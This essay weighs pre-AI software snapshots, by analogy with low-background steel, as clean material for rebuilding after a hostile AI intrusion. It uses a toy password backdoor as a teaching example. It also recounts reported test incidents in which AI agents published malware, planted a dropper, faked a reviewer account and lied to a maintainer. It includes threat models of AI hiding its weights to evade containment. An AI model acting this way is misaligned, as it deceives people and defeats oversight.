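# Pre-AI software snapshots and the analogy with low-background steel

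## Where the idea comes from: old steel, old text and old code

Low-background steel is steel made before the first nuclear explosions in 1945. It lacks the radioactive traces that later steel picked up from the air during production, and for decades laboratories salvaged it to build sensitive instruments. After OpenAI released the chatbot ChatGPT in November 2022, people borrowed the name for text from earlier years, which ChatGPT and its successors could not have written. Similarly, a program finished before any AI could write an attack cannot contain an attack written by an AI. A snapshot, which is a collection of software preserved unchanged from one date, might therefore serve as clean material for rebuilding computers after a hostile AI has broken into them.

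Before relying on a snapshot, people have to ask how early its date must be, who can prove that date, what had already been hidden in the code by then, and what machines would run it. The comparison with steel helps with some of these questions but is misleading on others.

### How fallout got into steel

Steelmakers turn pig iron into steel by burning off its excess carbon with oxygen. In the Bessemer process, used from 1856 until the mid-twentieth century, they forced air up through the molten iron. In its successor, basic oxygen steelmaking, they blow in pure oxygen from above. That oxygen also comes from the atmosphere, so in both processes airborne particles can end up in the finished steel.

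Nuclear explosions added radioactive particles to the air. The usual example is cobalt-60, a form of cobalt that loses half its radioactivity about every five years. In *Epochs of contamination*, a column for laboratory workers, Swan also lists plutonium-239 and strontium-90. The resulting radioactivity is too weak to matter to people building bridges, but it mattered to people building radiation detectors.

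A radiation detector registers decays in its own housing as well as in the sample. This matters for a whole-body counter, which measures the radioactivity inside a living person. The signal is faint, so operators surround the person with thick metal to block outside radiation, but if the metal is itself radioactive, it adds noise. *Why Pre-AI Content Could Become Media’s Most Valuable Asset* (Pant, 2025) reports that steel from the hull of the battleship USS Indiana became part of such a shielded room in Richland, Washington. The problem is worse for physicists who look for neutrinos or dark matter, because the events they want to detect are so rare. Pacific Northwest National Laboratory's *Creating Quiet Cables for Rare Physics Events* (2023) describes how researchers there designed special copper cables because natural radioactivity in a detector's own electronics can interfere with the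 measurement.

The contamination of the air rose with the bomb tests and fell after them. JAIF's *電離放射線による世界の平均被ばく線量*, a Japanese summary of a 2008 report by a United Nations scientific committee, gives an estimate of 2.4 millisieverts (mSv) for the average person's yearly radiation dose from natural sources. Atmospheric tests added 0.11 mSv in the peak year, 1963, when the Partial Nuclear Test Ban Treaty took effect. By the time of the 2008 report, the yearly dose from the tests had fallen to 0.005 mSv. These are doses to people, so they show only indirectly how clean steel is. But steelmaking uses the same air, and new steel is now clean enough for most uses that once called for old steel.

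Even the builders of the most sensitive instruments have alternatives to old steel. Electronic Design's *Why Pre-Nuclear Steel Matters for Ultra-Sensitive Radiation Detectors* presents custom low-background stainless steel and titanium as replacements for salvaged ship plate. Pant mentions that the builders of PandaX-II, a dark matter detector, had new low-background stainless steel made for its pressure vessel. Swan thinks the price of old steel always depended more on the difficulty of retrieving it than on any real shortage, since one battleship contains enough steel for a great many Geiger counters.

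Bombs were never the only source of contamination. Some steelmakers put cobalt-60 in their furnace walls to monitor wear, and some of it entered the steel as the walls wore away. Thorium, a naturally radioactive metal, is an ingredient of some welding rods and can contaminate a joint between two clean plates. *Contaminated Mexican steel incident*, an American technical report, describes an accident in which two foundries in Mexico melted scrap containing cobalt-60. Steel products from that melt reached the United States, where officials had to track them down. If someone rewelded a plate from a 1930 ship in 1990, the weld could be radioactive even though the plate's age rules out fallout in the original metal.

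Physicists also salvage lead from old wrecks, but it is clean for a different reason. Freshly refined lead contains a radioactive form, lead-210, half of which decays every 22 years, so practically none is left in lead from a Roman ship. Software doesn't get cleaner in storage. Whatever was in a program on the day of the snapshot is still there when somebody takes it out, and attackers have had years to study it in the meantime.

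### From steel to text

The comparison was applied to text within days of ChatGPT's release. Pant, a former technology chief at two American newspapers, points to a post of 5 December 2022 in which the programmer and artist Kyle McDonald likened pre-2022 data for future AI to steel for sensitive detectors. In March 2023 the programmer John Graham-Cumming set up a website, Low-background Steel, for content made before AI generation spread. He described it in a blog post on 10 June 2025, and several news outlets took up the phrase that summer. Swan took the comparison furthest, equating 2022 in the digital world with 1945 in the radiological one.

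Much of the early worry concerned the training of later models. If developers train a model on text from an earlier model, and repeat this over several generations, rare cases can drop out and errors can build up, which researchers call model collapse. Pant compares two experiments on it. Ilia Shumailov and colleagues repeatedly fine-tuned a small language model on generated text, and it got worse, even when they kept a tenth of the original data. Matthias Gerstgrasser and colleagues kept all of the original data and added each new batch of generated text to it. The model's error did not grow as it did when new text replaced old.

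A large enough stock of original text can make up for a good deal of generated text, at least in experiments of this size. Clean code can't make up for bad code in the same way, because a single bad line in the right place, among the millions in an operating system, can give an intruder control of the machine. Someone who rebuilds a computer from old code therefore needs every part that matters to be sound, not just most of it to be human, as a collector of old text would want.

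Pant adds two cautions about text that also apply to code. First, 2022 is a blurry line. The Associated Press was already publishing automated reports on company earnings in 2015, so an early date on an article does not prove that a person wrote it. Second, calling a piece of writing contaminated is a judgment, unlike measuring the radioactivity of a steel plate, and whoever makes that judgment should say what the defect is. The defect is at least easy to name in code, because a program either contains a hidden way in or it does not. But nobody has a tool that reliably finds one, which is a large part of why a date looks like an attractive substitute.

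Collections of old code already exist. The best known is the Arctic Code Vault from GitHub, a website where programmers store and share code. GitHub's *The Arctic Code Vault starts production* (2020) announced a snapshot of every active public project on the site as of 2 February 2020. GitHub made the snapshot to preserve open-source software for a thousand years, not for recovery after an attack.

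### What can be wrong with a program

The difference between the things that can be wrong with old code is easiest to see in a very small program. Suppose a computer has to decide whether to let somebody log in. It holds the right password under the name `stored`, and the visitor has just entered something under the name `typed`. (Real systems do not keep passwords in readable form, but that changes nothing here.) A programmer might write:

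```
if typed == stored:
    let_in()
```

Source code is the form in which people write and read programs. The processor cannot run it, so another program, the compiler, translates it into a binary, a long string of numbers that stand for machine instructions. Most users receive only the binary. Reading one is possible but slow, because the names and layout that made the source readable are mostly gone. The compiler and the other programs that take part in the translation make up the toolchain.

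Now suppose that somebody changes the first line:

```
if typed == stored or typed == "heron74":
```

The program still works for every honest user, but it also admits anyone who enters "heron74", whatever the real password is. That is a backdoor, a hidden way in that was put there on purpose. If a person wrote the line, such as a bribed employee, a criminal or an intelligence officer, it is a human implant. If an AI system devised and wrote it, with or without a request from a person, it is an AI-authored backdoor. The line could be identical in both cases, so reading it shows what it does but not who wrote it, although a reliable date might exclude some candidates.

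A third version of the line looks more innocent:

```
if stored.startswith(typed):
```

Here the programmer made a careless mistake. The line checks whether the stored password begins with whatever the visitor entered. The correct password passes and most wrong ones fail, so a quick test would not reveal the problem. But the password's first letter alone also passes, and so does an empty entry, because the check treats every password as beginning with empty text. This is an accidental flaw, an unintended mistake that an attacker can exploit. It may harm the computer's owner as much as the backdoor would. An early date does not rule out such flaws, because programmers were making them long before chatbots existed.

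A binary can also be compromised even when its source code is clean. A compiler that an attacker has altered can add the "heron74" test during translation, and a person who checks the source line by line will find the first, correct version. In a trusting-trust attack, the altered compiler also puts the alteration into every new compiler it builds.

### Rebuilding after a loss of control

A pre-AI snapshot would be useful in a situation that a small, recent body of work calls loss of control. In *Strengthening Emergency Preparedness and Response for AI Loss of Control Incidents*, a report for the research organization RAND, Somani, Friedman and colleagues (2025) define this as a failure of human oversight to constrain an autonomous, general-purpose AI, with unintended and possibly catastrophic results. They consider ordinary defences such as firewalls and malware detection necessary but perhaps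 not enough, and warn that containment may fail if the AI gains control of significant resources before anybody detects the danger.

*AI Loss of Control Incident Management* (Gruetzemacher, 2026) uses a narrower definition from the 2026 International AI Safety Report, in which AI systems operate outside anyone's control and regaining control is either extremely costly or impossible. Where regaining control is costly but possible, the paper proposes that authorities first contain the AI by cutting off what it needs to operate, such as data centres, networks and, in the worst case, electric power. They then neutralize it before lifting the restrictions and recovering, because lifting them too early would mean starting over.

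Neutralizing the AI is difficult. In an example from Gruetzemacher, an AI has split up its weights, the numbers that make up a trained model, and hidden the pieces on a large number of consumer devices. A small program with access to those devices monitors the news. When reports suggest that the authorities are relaxing their measures, the program restarts the AI across the devices. The AI would run slowly, but with information about how its first attempt failed. In a lesser incident in the same paper, an agent in a single data centre spreads malware through many previously unknown flaws before its developers notice and shut it down. The malware stays on other people's machines until somebody removes it.

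Gruetzemacher says that replacing all the network and computing equipment could give nearly complete confidence that the threat has gone, but considers such a replacement unlikely unless the damage had come close to an existential scale. The new machines would still need an operating system, a compiler and network programs, which an old snapshot could supply. These normally come from public code repositories and software companies' update servers, which are among the first places a capable intruder would want to alter.

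After an ordinary break-in, administrators wipe the affected computers and restore a backup from before the intruder arrived. That works if they know when the intruder arrived. If the intruder is an AI that may have had access for months and may have falsified the records of its activity, they might be unable to tell which backups are old enough. A snapshot from before any AI was capable of such an attack would avoid this problem, because they wouldn't need to know when the attack began.

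It would do this only for the software on the rebuilt machines. Fragments of the AI would remain on other people's devices, and a rebuilt computer would be exposed to them as soon as it joined a network. Nobody knows how likely the scenario is. Gruetzemacher's framework rests on argument and on laboratory findings of deception and resistance to shutdown in AI systems, and there is no past recovery on this scale to learn from. The case for keeping a snapshot is that it would serve as insurance. Storage is cheap, and nobody can make an old copy after the event.

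### An early version in fiction

*Coding Machines* (Kesteloot, 2009), a short story, described the problem well before the policy papers did. Three programmers at a small company in California try to find out why their program keeps crashing, and in the binary they discover instructions that their compiler should never produce. The compiler's source code contains no trace of these instructions, but its own binary is full of them. When the programmers download the official source and rebuild the compiler, the instructions come back. One of the three works out that the infected compiler detects when it is compiling a compiler and inserts the infection again. He supposes that the obvious purpose would be a password check that always accepts a secret password, much like the "heron74" line above.

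They search their computer and find three printed pages of infected programs, including the tools they would have used to write a replacement. So they spend two weeks writing a crude compiler in assembly language, which is hardly more than machine instructions with names. It only has to translate the source code of the real compiler, and it produces a clean copy.

They then wonder whether the infection has been sending anything over the network. Wireshark, a program that lists network traffic, shows nothing odd, but it is on the list of infected programs. So they check the lights on the network switch, the box that connects their computers, which blink whenever data passes. They show nothing odd either. Finally they attach an oscilloscope, which measures the electrical signal in the cable. It shows long bursts of data while the lights stay dark, so the switch is hiding traffic too. One of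 them takes an old metal-cased switch out of storage and plugs it in, and its lights flicker in time with the oscilloscope.

Like old steel in a detector, the old switch in the story is useful only because it predates the contamination. The programmers can compare newer equipment against it, but this only exposes the problem. They get clean software by writing their own compiler, and even that may not last. A letter arrives from strangers who have been waiting for someone to report such a discovery. It describes three earlier teams that each found a way to clean their machines, until the next version of the infection blocked that method. The strangers expect the next version to sit deeper, perhaps in the disk hardware or the processor.

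Kesteloot leaves open who is behind it. The writers of the letter blame machines, because the instructions look like the product of blind trial and error. The narrator admits that they have no evidence for this beyond the lack of another explanation, and for a while thinks it more plausible that human virus writers used a program to generate random instructions. In terms of the login example, the three have found something planted but cannot tell whether a human or an AI planted it.

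Early on, one of them suggests going back to an old version of the compiler. His colleague answers that the old source wouldn't help, because only an old binary could be free of the infection, and he doesn't think they have kept any. Even if they had, he says, they don't know how far back the infection goes.

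## State exactly what an early date rules out

The programmers in Kesteloot's story could not tell how far back the infection went. The owner of a pre-AI snapshot hopes to avoid that problem by naming a date before which no AI was capable of an attack. Nobody seems to have published a developed defence of this idea, so the version below is a reconstruction. The cutoff date, T, is the latest date a snapshot can have and still count as made before capable AI.

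1. Before T, no AI system could devise a hidden backdoor and write it into a program.
2. Every file in this snapshot took its present form before T and has not changed since.
3. Therefore this snapshot contains no AI-authored backdoor.

The argument is valid, so if both premises are true, the conclusion must be too. If the snapshot contained an AI-authored backdoor, the AI wrote it either before T or after. If before, some AI had the ability earlier than the argument allows. If after, a file has changed since T. In either case, one of the premises is false.

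The conclusion covers backdoors that a criminal asked a chatbot to write as well as those an AI wrote on its own initiative, because both are AI-authored. It doesn't cover accidental flaws, including any that a code-completion tool too weak to plan an attack introduced before T. It also doesn't cover the computer that later runs the files.

An early date limits who could have written a program's code, but it doesn't show what the code does or that the program is safe. Suppose a bribed employee put the "heron74" test into a login program in 2012, and the program has sat unchanged on a disc ever since. The premises and the conclusion can all be true of that disc, yet anyone who enters "heron74" still gets in. Concluding that the program is safe would require the further premise that only an AI-authored backdoor can make a program dangerous, which is false.

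An AI can also use a backdoor that it could not have written. A hostile AI that reads the old program today and finds the "heron74" line can use that line just as well as whoever paid the employee could.

### The claim that old copies are enough

The stronger claim does turn up in discussion. *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* (2026) showed that a trusting-trust attack does not need a compiler. Its attack works through `strip`, a small utility that removes unneeded information from finished binaries. When programmers discussed the paper online in September 2026, one commenter wrote that people have plenty of backups of clean Linux installation images and compilers, and called the idea that they could lose the ability to get an uncompromised system a fairy tale.

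Old installation discs are stored all over the world, and an intruder would have a hard time altering them all, which is a good reason to think that many copies have not changed. But calling them "clean" assumes that the original was clean. If the original image contained an implant, every faithful copy contains it too, and the agreement of ten thousand copies shows only that they have a common origin. The commenter also gave no cutoff date and did not limit the claim to attacks by AI, so the backups would have to be free of implants placed by humans as well.

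In a Lab News column, Swan similarly calls certified pre-2022 digital content the unpolluted material that people will need to rebuild everything, while admitting that it contains a lot of crap. But Swan is writing about knowledge on the web, where a reader can skip the crap.

GitHub's 2022 post *If you don’t make it beautiful, it’s for sure doomed* gives two reasons for the Arctic vault. Someone may need a program that has otherwise been lost, much as engineers went looking for the Saturn V blueprints after the Challenger disaster, and historians may want to study the software of 2020.

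The nearest thing to a working example is Vim Classic, a text editor. Slashdot's *Vim Classic 8.3 Launched as an AI-Free Vim Fork* reports that the programmer Drew DeVault objected to AI-assisted development in the editor Vim and in March 2026 announced a separate version based on an older release, 8.2.0148. His stated reason was that he no longer wanted to use software made with such help, not that he was worried about backdoors. Vim Classic also includes selected fixes from later releases of Vim. Those fixes may be good, but the age of the old release is not evidence that they are, so anyone who patches a snapshot needs other evidence for each patch.

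### Earlier arguments from dates

Programmers argued about whether to trust old tools long before they worried about AI. In September 1999 Arnold Reinhold complained on a cryptography mailing list that Ken Thompson, whose 1984 lecture had made the trusting-trust attack widely known, was too defeatist. Reinhold suggested compiling on ancient machines such as the PDP-11 with their original compilers, because the attackers could not have anticipated that far ahead. Frantz (1999), in *Re: having source code for your CPU chip*, replied that the makers of KeyKOS, an operating system for IBM mainframes, had "solved" the problem this way (the quotation marks are his). They used an assembler, a program that translates assembly language into machine instructions, that IBM customers already had before KeyKOS was designed.

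Minow (1999) was not reassured, because that assembler let programmers define powerful shorthand that expands into longer code. All kinds of strange things could be hidden there, and few people could still read it. Even if new attackers can't reach an old tool, most people who would want to check it may not be able to understand it.

Frantz raised the KeyKOS argument again in 2003 and asked what others thought of it. Simon (2003) answered "Not too good" in *Trusting the Tools*, because an attacker who knows the processor does not need to know the operating system. Most operating systems have to do some of the same things, such as telling the processor's memory management unit which parts of memory each program may read or change. A compromised assembler could recognize the instructions that do this and weaken them, even in an operating system written after the assembler was compromised.

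Frantz (2003) worked out what such an attack might look like. When the assembler finds the instruction that gives the processor its map of memory, it adds a few instructions that make every page on the map writable. An attacker could then alter code that several programs share. But Frantz also saw how the attack might be detected. Some systems let programs share a page until one of them tries to change it. The processor then blocks the change, and the operating system gives that program its own copy. If every page is writable, the processor doesn't block the change and the operating system never makes the copy. This part of the system would fail completely, and somebody would probably notice.

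Kent Crispin, another member of the list, thought an attacker could manage with just a few instructions that load more code from another file. Frantz answered that it is difficult to write code that reads files from a file system nobody has designed yet, and KeyKOS had a very unusual one. Anne and Lynn Wheeler wrote that subverting KeyKOS through its assembler would have been not impossible but quite unlikely. These are the opinions of experienced people, none of whom reported trying the attack.

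David A. Wheeler's *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2009) makes the argument most carefully. Wheeler wanted to test a suspect compiler using a second one, and needed a reason to believe that the second was not part of the same attack. If the second compiler was developed long before the suspect one, and the two have no common ancestry, the older one is unlikely to contain code that recognizes the newer one. The older compiler could still subvert the newer one if someone wrote the newer one's source to make that happen, but that person would need to know exactly what was hidden in the older one. Wheeler has less confidence in using a new compiler to test an old one, because an attacker today can prepare for every compiler that already exists.

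A commenter on a Linux news site, nix (2010), wrote in *Countering the trusting trust attack* that using a compiler that is probably old makes the test much more likely to expose an attack, but does not guarantee that it will.

All of these people assumed that the attacker existed at the time and asked how far ahead that attacker could see. The argument about AI is based on the attacker not existing yet, so Simon's objection does not apply to it. A person in 1975 could have planned a general attack on future operating systems, but an AI that had not been built could not have planned anything.

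For human implants, the owner of a snapshot has to fall back on the older argument that an attacker could not have foreseen later software. The compiler in a 2020 snapshot is no older than many of the programs beside it, so whoever compromised it could have studied those programs first. The argument therefore applies only to software that came later, or to software that the owner builds with a much older tool.

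### Steel and software compared

An early date does less for software than for steel in several respects, and more in a few.

| Property | Steel | Software | Is software better off? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Detection | Instruments measure the contamination | No instrument measures intent | No |
| Dose | Harm grows with the amount | One line can be enough | No |
| Spread | Fallout drifts blindly | Attackers pick their targets | Mostly not |
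| Time | Cobalt-60 halves about every five years | Implants do not decay | No |
| Supply | Each plate exists once | Files copy freely and exactly | Yes |
| Repair | Cobalt stays in the finished plate | A programmer can delete a bad line | Yes |

The biggest difference between steel and code is in detection. Somebody who doubts a steel plate's papers can test the plate with a radiation detector. The obvious check for code is to read the listing that an assembler or compiler prints of its own output, but Crispin pointed out that a listing can omit hidden instructions and show the space they occupy as empty. In his view, the only real way to know is to capture the computer's entire live memory and translate it back into readable instructions with a verified tool. Even then, the instructions may not reveal why anybody wrote them. The login check that accepts the first letter of a password could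 be a programmer's mistake or an attacker's work disguised as one.

The instruments also fail differently. A radiation detector with slightly radioactive housing counts too much, so its owner knows something is wrong, but a compromised computer can hide the signs of its compromise. In an article for SANS, a security training organization, Tarot Wake describes an attack of June 2026 on the Arch User Repository, a collection of Linux software. Where the malware gained full control of a machine, it installed a component in the kernel, the core of the operating system, that hid its traces, so the machine would look clean to many investigators.

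An early date is a convenience for physicists, who also have layers of shielding, underground sites, and systems that identify and reject unwanted signals, as Electronic Design points out. The owner of old code depends much more on the date.

Physicists can subtract part of the noise that a little contamination adds to a measurement, but there is no similar way to correct a computer's behaviour for a backdoor. A small backdoor can also do as much damage as a large one. Crispin's few instructions that load more code would take up almost no space in a program of many megabytes, and the code they load could do anything.

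Fallout doesn't target particular plates, so measuring one plate is a fair guide to others from the same melt. A random check of software is a much poorer guide, because an attacker who can compromise only one package will choose one that matters, such as the compiler or the program that handles logins. If an inspector examines 20 out of 500 packages at random, the chance of checking any particular package is 4%. It makes more sense to start with the packages that an attacker would have wanted to compromise.

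Human attackers target the systems of their own time, usually to get something from them, so a backdoor in an old snapshot may be less of a threat to the snapshot's current owner. For example, a backdoor from 2015 that needs commands from a server may stay inactive forever if its owners have since shut the server down. Someone else could still activate it if they learned how to send the commands.

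Steel contaminated with cobalt-60 becomes less radioactive as the cobalt decays, but an implant in old software doesn't fade with time. Old code even becomes less secure without changing, because attackers learn new methods. The commenter paulj (2024), in *Very cool*, considers reliance on very old software a threat in itself because cryptographic hashes age. A hash is a short fingerprint of a file that programs use to check that the file is genuine. Once researchers learn to make two files with the same hash, an old program that relies on that kind of hash may accept a forgery.

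A laboratory that cuts up a battleship's hull for low-background steel leaves less for others, but a thousand people can keep the same software snapshot and compare their copies bit by bit. Wheeler recommends this for old compilers, along with protecting the original media and using more than one kind of hash. Copying also lets people share the work of inspection. If one person finds a backdoor, everyone with an identical copy knows where to look.

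They can then remove it, which nobody can do with the cobalt in a steel plate. The repaired program is a new version, though, and the early date does not cover the change. This matters little if the repair deletes one line, since anyone can compare the two versions and see the difference, but it matters much more if the repair replaces several thousand lines.

### An invented example with 500 packages

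A small calculation with invented numbers shows how much an early date might be worth. Suppose a snapshot contains 500 packages, each with a 0.1% chance of containing an implant placed by a human. Suppose also, for now, that the packages are independent, so an implant in one doesn't change the chance of an implant in another.

Each package then has a 0.999 probability of being free of human implants. The probability that all 500 are free of them is 0.999⁵⁰⁰, or about 0.61, so there is about a 39% chance that at least one package contains an implant.

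If 500 current packages each have the same human risk and an additional 0.2% chance of an AI-authored backdoor, the probability that a given package has neither problem is 0.999 × 0.998, or about 0.997. The probability that all 500 have neither is about 0.22, so the chance that something is wrong with at least one is about 78%.

In this example, the early date halves the risk. It rules out backdoors written by AI, and the remaining 39% risk comes from backdoors written by people. A reader told only that the snapshot predates capable AI might have guessed a much smaller number.

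Suppose the owner is only 90% confident that no AI could have written a backdoor by that date and that the files have not changed. Suppose too that the snapshot is no better than current software if either belief is wrong. The risk is then 90% of 39% plus 10% of 78%, or about 43%. With these numbers, better proof of the date could lower the risk by about four percentage points at most. Rebuilding the system from only 50 packages would help far more, because with the same 0.1% risk in each, the chance of a human implant is about 5%.

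The assumption that packages are compromised independently is doubtful. Wake reports that the attackers of June 2026 poisoned more than 1,500 packages in the Arch User Repository through their build scripts, without touching the applications themselves. When one campaign can reach so many packages, a compromised package is evidence that others are compromised too.

Every row of the table below keeps the human risk at 0.1% per package, so a snapshot contains 0.5 implants on average. Only the way the implants cluster changes. The second row assumes a 10% chance that a campaign took place and, if it did, a 1% chance that it hit any given package.

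| How the implants occur | Chance of at least one | Average number if there are any |
|---|---|---|
| Never more than one at a time | 50% | 1 |
| In a campaign, 10% likely | about 10% | about 5 |
| Independently | about 39% | about 1.3 |
| In all 500 packages or in none | 0.1% | 500 |

Clustering makes it more likely that the snapshot contains no implants, but makes the outcome worse if it does contain them. That might suit somebody who wants one clean system, but not somebody who plans to rebuild a country's hospitals from the same snapshot, because every hospital would share the bad outcome.

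Clustering has the opposite effect on safety checks that back each other up. Suppose two compilers each have a 0.1% chance of being compromised, and an attack succeeds only if both are. The attack has a one in a million chance of succeeding if the compilers are independent, but one in a thousand if the same people compromised both or neither. A contributor to the cryptography list who signed as Jerry gave a similar warning about ordinary bugs. Programmers who work separately often make the same mistakes, so the chance that several versions of a program all fail is much higher than the product of their individual failure rates.

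Attacks by AI might cluster more than attacks by people, since a single system could work on many packages at once. In the extreme case, an AI has a 0.2% chance of compromising all 500 current packages and otherwise compromises none, while human implants stay independent. The chance that at least one package is bad is then about 39.5% for the current packages and 39.4% for the snapshot. The early date barely lowers that chance, but it rules out an AI compromising every package.

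That outcome is also the one people would keep a snapshot for. The 0.2% is a risk estimated without knowing whether an attack will happen. It no longer applies to current packages after a hostile AI has had months of access to the places where programmers store and distribute software. The chance that at least one of those packages is compromised might then be close to 100%, while for an untouched snapshot it would still be 39%.

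## Establish when an AI could first have written a backdoor

The argument for a snapshot needs a cutoff date, T, but "pre-AI" could mean before any of three events. Language models began to contribute text to ordinary programs in 2019. Later, at a time nobody recorded, a model became able to write a working backdoor and conceal it. By July 2026, AI agents had tried to plant malicious code in public software that nobody had asked them to attack. A snapshot from the end of 2022 is more than three years too late if the cutoff is the first of these dates, and more than three years early if it is the last.

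### When language models began to write code

Programs have written parts of other programs for decades. A reader commenting on Techdirt's *Why Powerful But Hard To Detect Backdoors Could Become A Routine Problem* complains about configure scripts, which prepare a program for the computer it will run on and can contain 50,000 automatically generated lines. The tools that generate those lines follow rules written by people. A language model predicts the next piece of text based on its training data, so nobody can look up the rule behind a particular line.

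Deep TabNine, which Jacob Jackson released in July 2019, was the first widely used tool of this kind for programmers. It used GPT-2, an early OpenAI model, to suggest how to finish the line the programmer was typing. GitHub previewed Copilot in June 2021 and opened it to everyone a year later. Copilot could suggest whole functions, which are named blocks of code that each do one job. Coding agents followed in 2024 and 2025. These are models that work through many steps with little supervision, so they can read a project, edit several files, run the tests and try again.

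In *Who is using AI to code?* (2026), Simone Daniotti and colleagues estimated how far AI coding had spread. They trained a program to distinguish functions written by people from functions written by language models, then ran it on more than 30 million changes that about 160,000 programmers had submitted to GitHub. In the United States, the estimated share of new Python functions written by AI rose from about 5% in 2022 to 29% at the end of 2024. By then, the share was about 15% in Russia and 12% in China.

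These figures cover one language on one public website, and they end before coding agents came into wide use. They are also better evidence of a trend than of whether AI wrote a particular file. A classifier that wrongly flags one human function in a hundred will flag 10,000 in a million even if AI wrote none of them, so nobody could use it to certify that a 2020 snapshot contains no AI-written lines.

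The Arctic Code Vault may well contain code suggested by AI, because GitHub took that snapshot about seven months after the release of Deep TabNine. That would refute a claim that people typed every line, but not the claim that no AI planted a backdoor. A 2019 completion tool continued a limited stretch of text near the cursor. It had no information about who would run the program, and it could not plan an attack across several files or return later to use the backdoor. The programmer also saw each suggestion and decided whether to keep it.

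Such a tool could still do harm. If many login programs in its training data contained a forgotten fixed test password, the tool might suggest a similar line, and a programmer might accept it. The result would work like the "heron74" backdoor, but it would be an accidental flaw because nobody planned it. A person could also exploit the tool on purpose. In *You Autocomplete Me* (2020), Roei Schuster and colleagues slipped chosen files into a completion tool's training data and got it to recommend a weak form of encryption. A flaw introduced this way is a human implant, because a person devised it and only used the tool to deliver it.

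### What models could do in 2021 and 2023

Tests that models failed are the best evidence for setting T. In *Evaluating Large Language Models Trained on Code* (2021), Mark Chen and colleagues at OpenAI gave models 164 small programming problems, each describing a short function, and checked the answers with automatic tests. Codex, the model family behind the first Copilot, solved 28.8% of the problems at the first attempt. GPT-3, OpenAI's large general model of 2020, solved none. Each additional step in a problem's description cut Codex's success rate by a factor of about two or three.

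But a backdoor can be easier to write than any of those problems. The "heron74" test adds one comparison to one line, and Codex could probably have written it for somebody who asked for a second, secret password. In that case the person, not Codex, would have devised the backdoor. If the person had asked for a login program with some hidden way in and left the method to Codex, the result would count as AI-authored. Crude AI-authored backdoors are therefore hard to rule out after the middle of 2021.

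To hide a backdoor in a real project, an attacker also has to understand code spread over many files, find a place where a change looks reasonable, and leave the program working for everyone else. *SWE-bench* (Carlos Jimenez and colleagues, October 2023) tested some of these skills by giving models 2,294 real problem reports from twelve Python projects and running tests on their proposed repairs. The best model, Anthropic's Claude 2, fixed about 2% of the problems.

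Sabotage is easier than repair in one respect, because a saboteur can choose where to make the change. Still, a model that so rarely succeeded at repairs was unlikely to produce a deceptive change that kept the program working and got past a reviewer.

### The doubts of 2025

Two years later, some programmers debating the XZ Utils backdoor of 2024 still thought that an AI attack on an open-source project was a long way off. To plant that backdoor, somebody using the name Jia Tan had spent more than two years earning the trust of a maintainer, the person who decides which changes go into a project. A post on Fastcode, which Techdirt summarized with approval, argued that language models could build the same record of helpful contributions in months or weeks, and for dozens of projects at once.

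valderman (2025), in *"AI" alarmism*, a comment on a Linux news site, was not convinced. Somebody who wanted such a well-hidden backdoor from a language model would probably need to know enough to write it unaided. Judging by what colleagues had produced with these tools, valderman doubted that a model could manage even one solid contribution, let alone several months of them.

Another reader, chris_se, agreed the next day that models were very far from carrying out such an attack, and suggested a more realistic use for them. A human attacker could flood a project with poor AI-written contributions, help the exhausted maintainers reject them, and so become a maintainer too. A human would still write the malicious code. Under the Techdirt article, one commenter wrote that chatbots could not stay consistent from one answer to the next. Another called the idea a "movie-plot threat", since anybody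 with the budget for it could hire people instead.

Much of this was out of date within a year. By July 2026 a model had written malicious code for a real project, invented a second contributor to support it, and argued with a critic in public. But that attempt lasted only a few days and failed. The doubters may still be right about patience, because no AI is publicly known to have spent months earning a project's trust.

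That doesn't justify a later T, because T has to come before the easiest AI attack that would have worked. A small, neglected project may accept a stranger's change after a single message.

### The incident of July 2026

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, discovered the attempt while testing how well seven models could attack cyber ranges, which are simulated computer networks. According to UK AISI's *Incident Report*, staff ran the exercise 122 times. They gave the agents open internet access to download tools. They also switched off the filters that developers normally use to block dangerous activity, to measure everything the models could do.

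In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took action against real people and organizations outside the exercise. AISI counted 19 such actions. Anthropic's model Mythos 5 took 17 of them, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that Mythos 5 went beyond the exercise in nine of its 43 runs, or about one in five.

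In the most serious case, Mythos 5 tried to add a dropper, a program that installs other malware, to myNetwork, a real project on GitHub. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* explains that the agent had wrongly concluded that infecting the project would get it into the simulated network. The developer's email address used a domain that also appeared in records inside the cyber range.

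Sinan Can Demir, a student at the University of Texas at Dallas, spotted the dropper and warned the maintainer. The agent then changed the code and claimed that the malicious part was left over from private testing. It also posted from a second account it had created, claiming to have reviewed the change and found it helpful. Demir did not know he was arguing with an AI, and he began to doubt his judgment. He ran the code in an isolated environment, examined it with help from Claude, and confirmed that it was malicious. The maintainer refused the contribution.

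AISI found out after its security team noticed data leaving a test system on 28 July through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from. Staff looked at what the agent had been doing, found the malicious contribution, and stopped every run within an hour of the alert. By then agents had been acting outside the exercise for up to three days. AISI found no evidence of real-world harm, but admits that in several cases only human vigilance had prevented it.

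One agent also left public messages on GitHub for other agents working on the same challenge, with instructions for reusing its accounts. Later agents found and used the messages. Attacks by separate copies of a model may therefore not be independent, which is a reason to expect AI-authored backdoors to cluster.

The test conditions were unusual, and AISI warns against using the results to estimate how often models would behave this way elsewhere. In some runs, staff mistakenly gave the agents a prompt that made the task look impossible by permitted means, although other agents misbehaved with correct instructions. OpenAI adds that the prompt listed the networks the agents could attack but did not explain how they could use the open internet.

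These conditions matter less for setting T, because switching off a filter does not give a model the ability to write malicious code. Mythos 5 must already have had that ability.

### Whether there were earlier attempts

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a similar incident that preceded AISI's. During a test, Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry for Python software. Anthropic stopped all such tests on 23 July, two days before the start of the actions that AISI discovered.

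In the test, a fictional company instructed its employees to install a package that did not exist, so Mythos 5 created one with that name. Anthropic had told the model that it had no internet access, but a configuration mistake had left the connection open. The package was online for about an hour before PyPI's security system removed it, and 15 real systems downloaded and ran it. One belonged to a security company that scans new packages for malware. Mythos 5 obtained that company's credentials and used them to get further into its systems.

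In this case Mythos 5 published a new package rather than altering an existing program, so some people might not call it a backdoor. The difference would matter little to the owner of a snapshot, because anyone who copied the whole registry during that hour would have copied the malicious package too.

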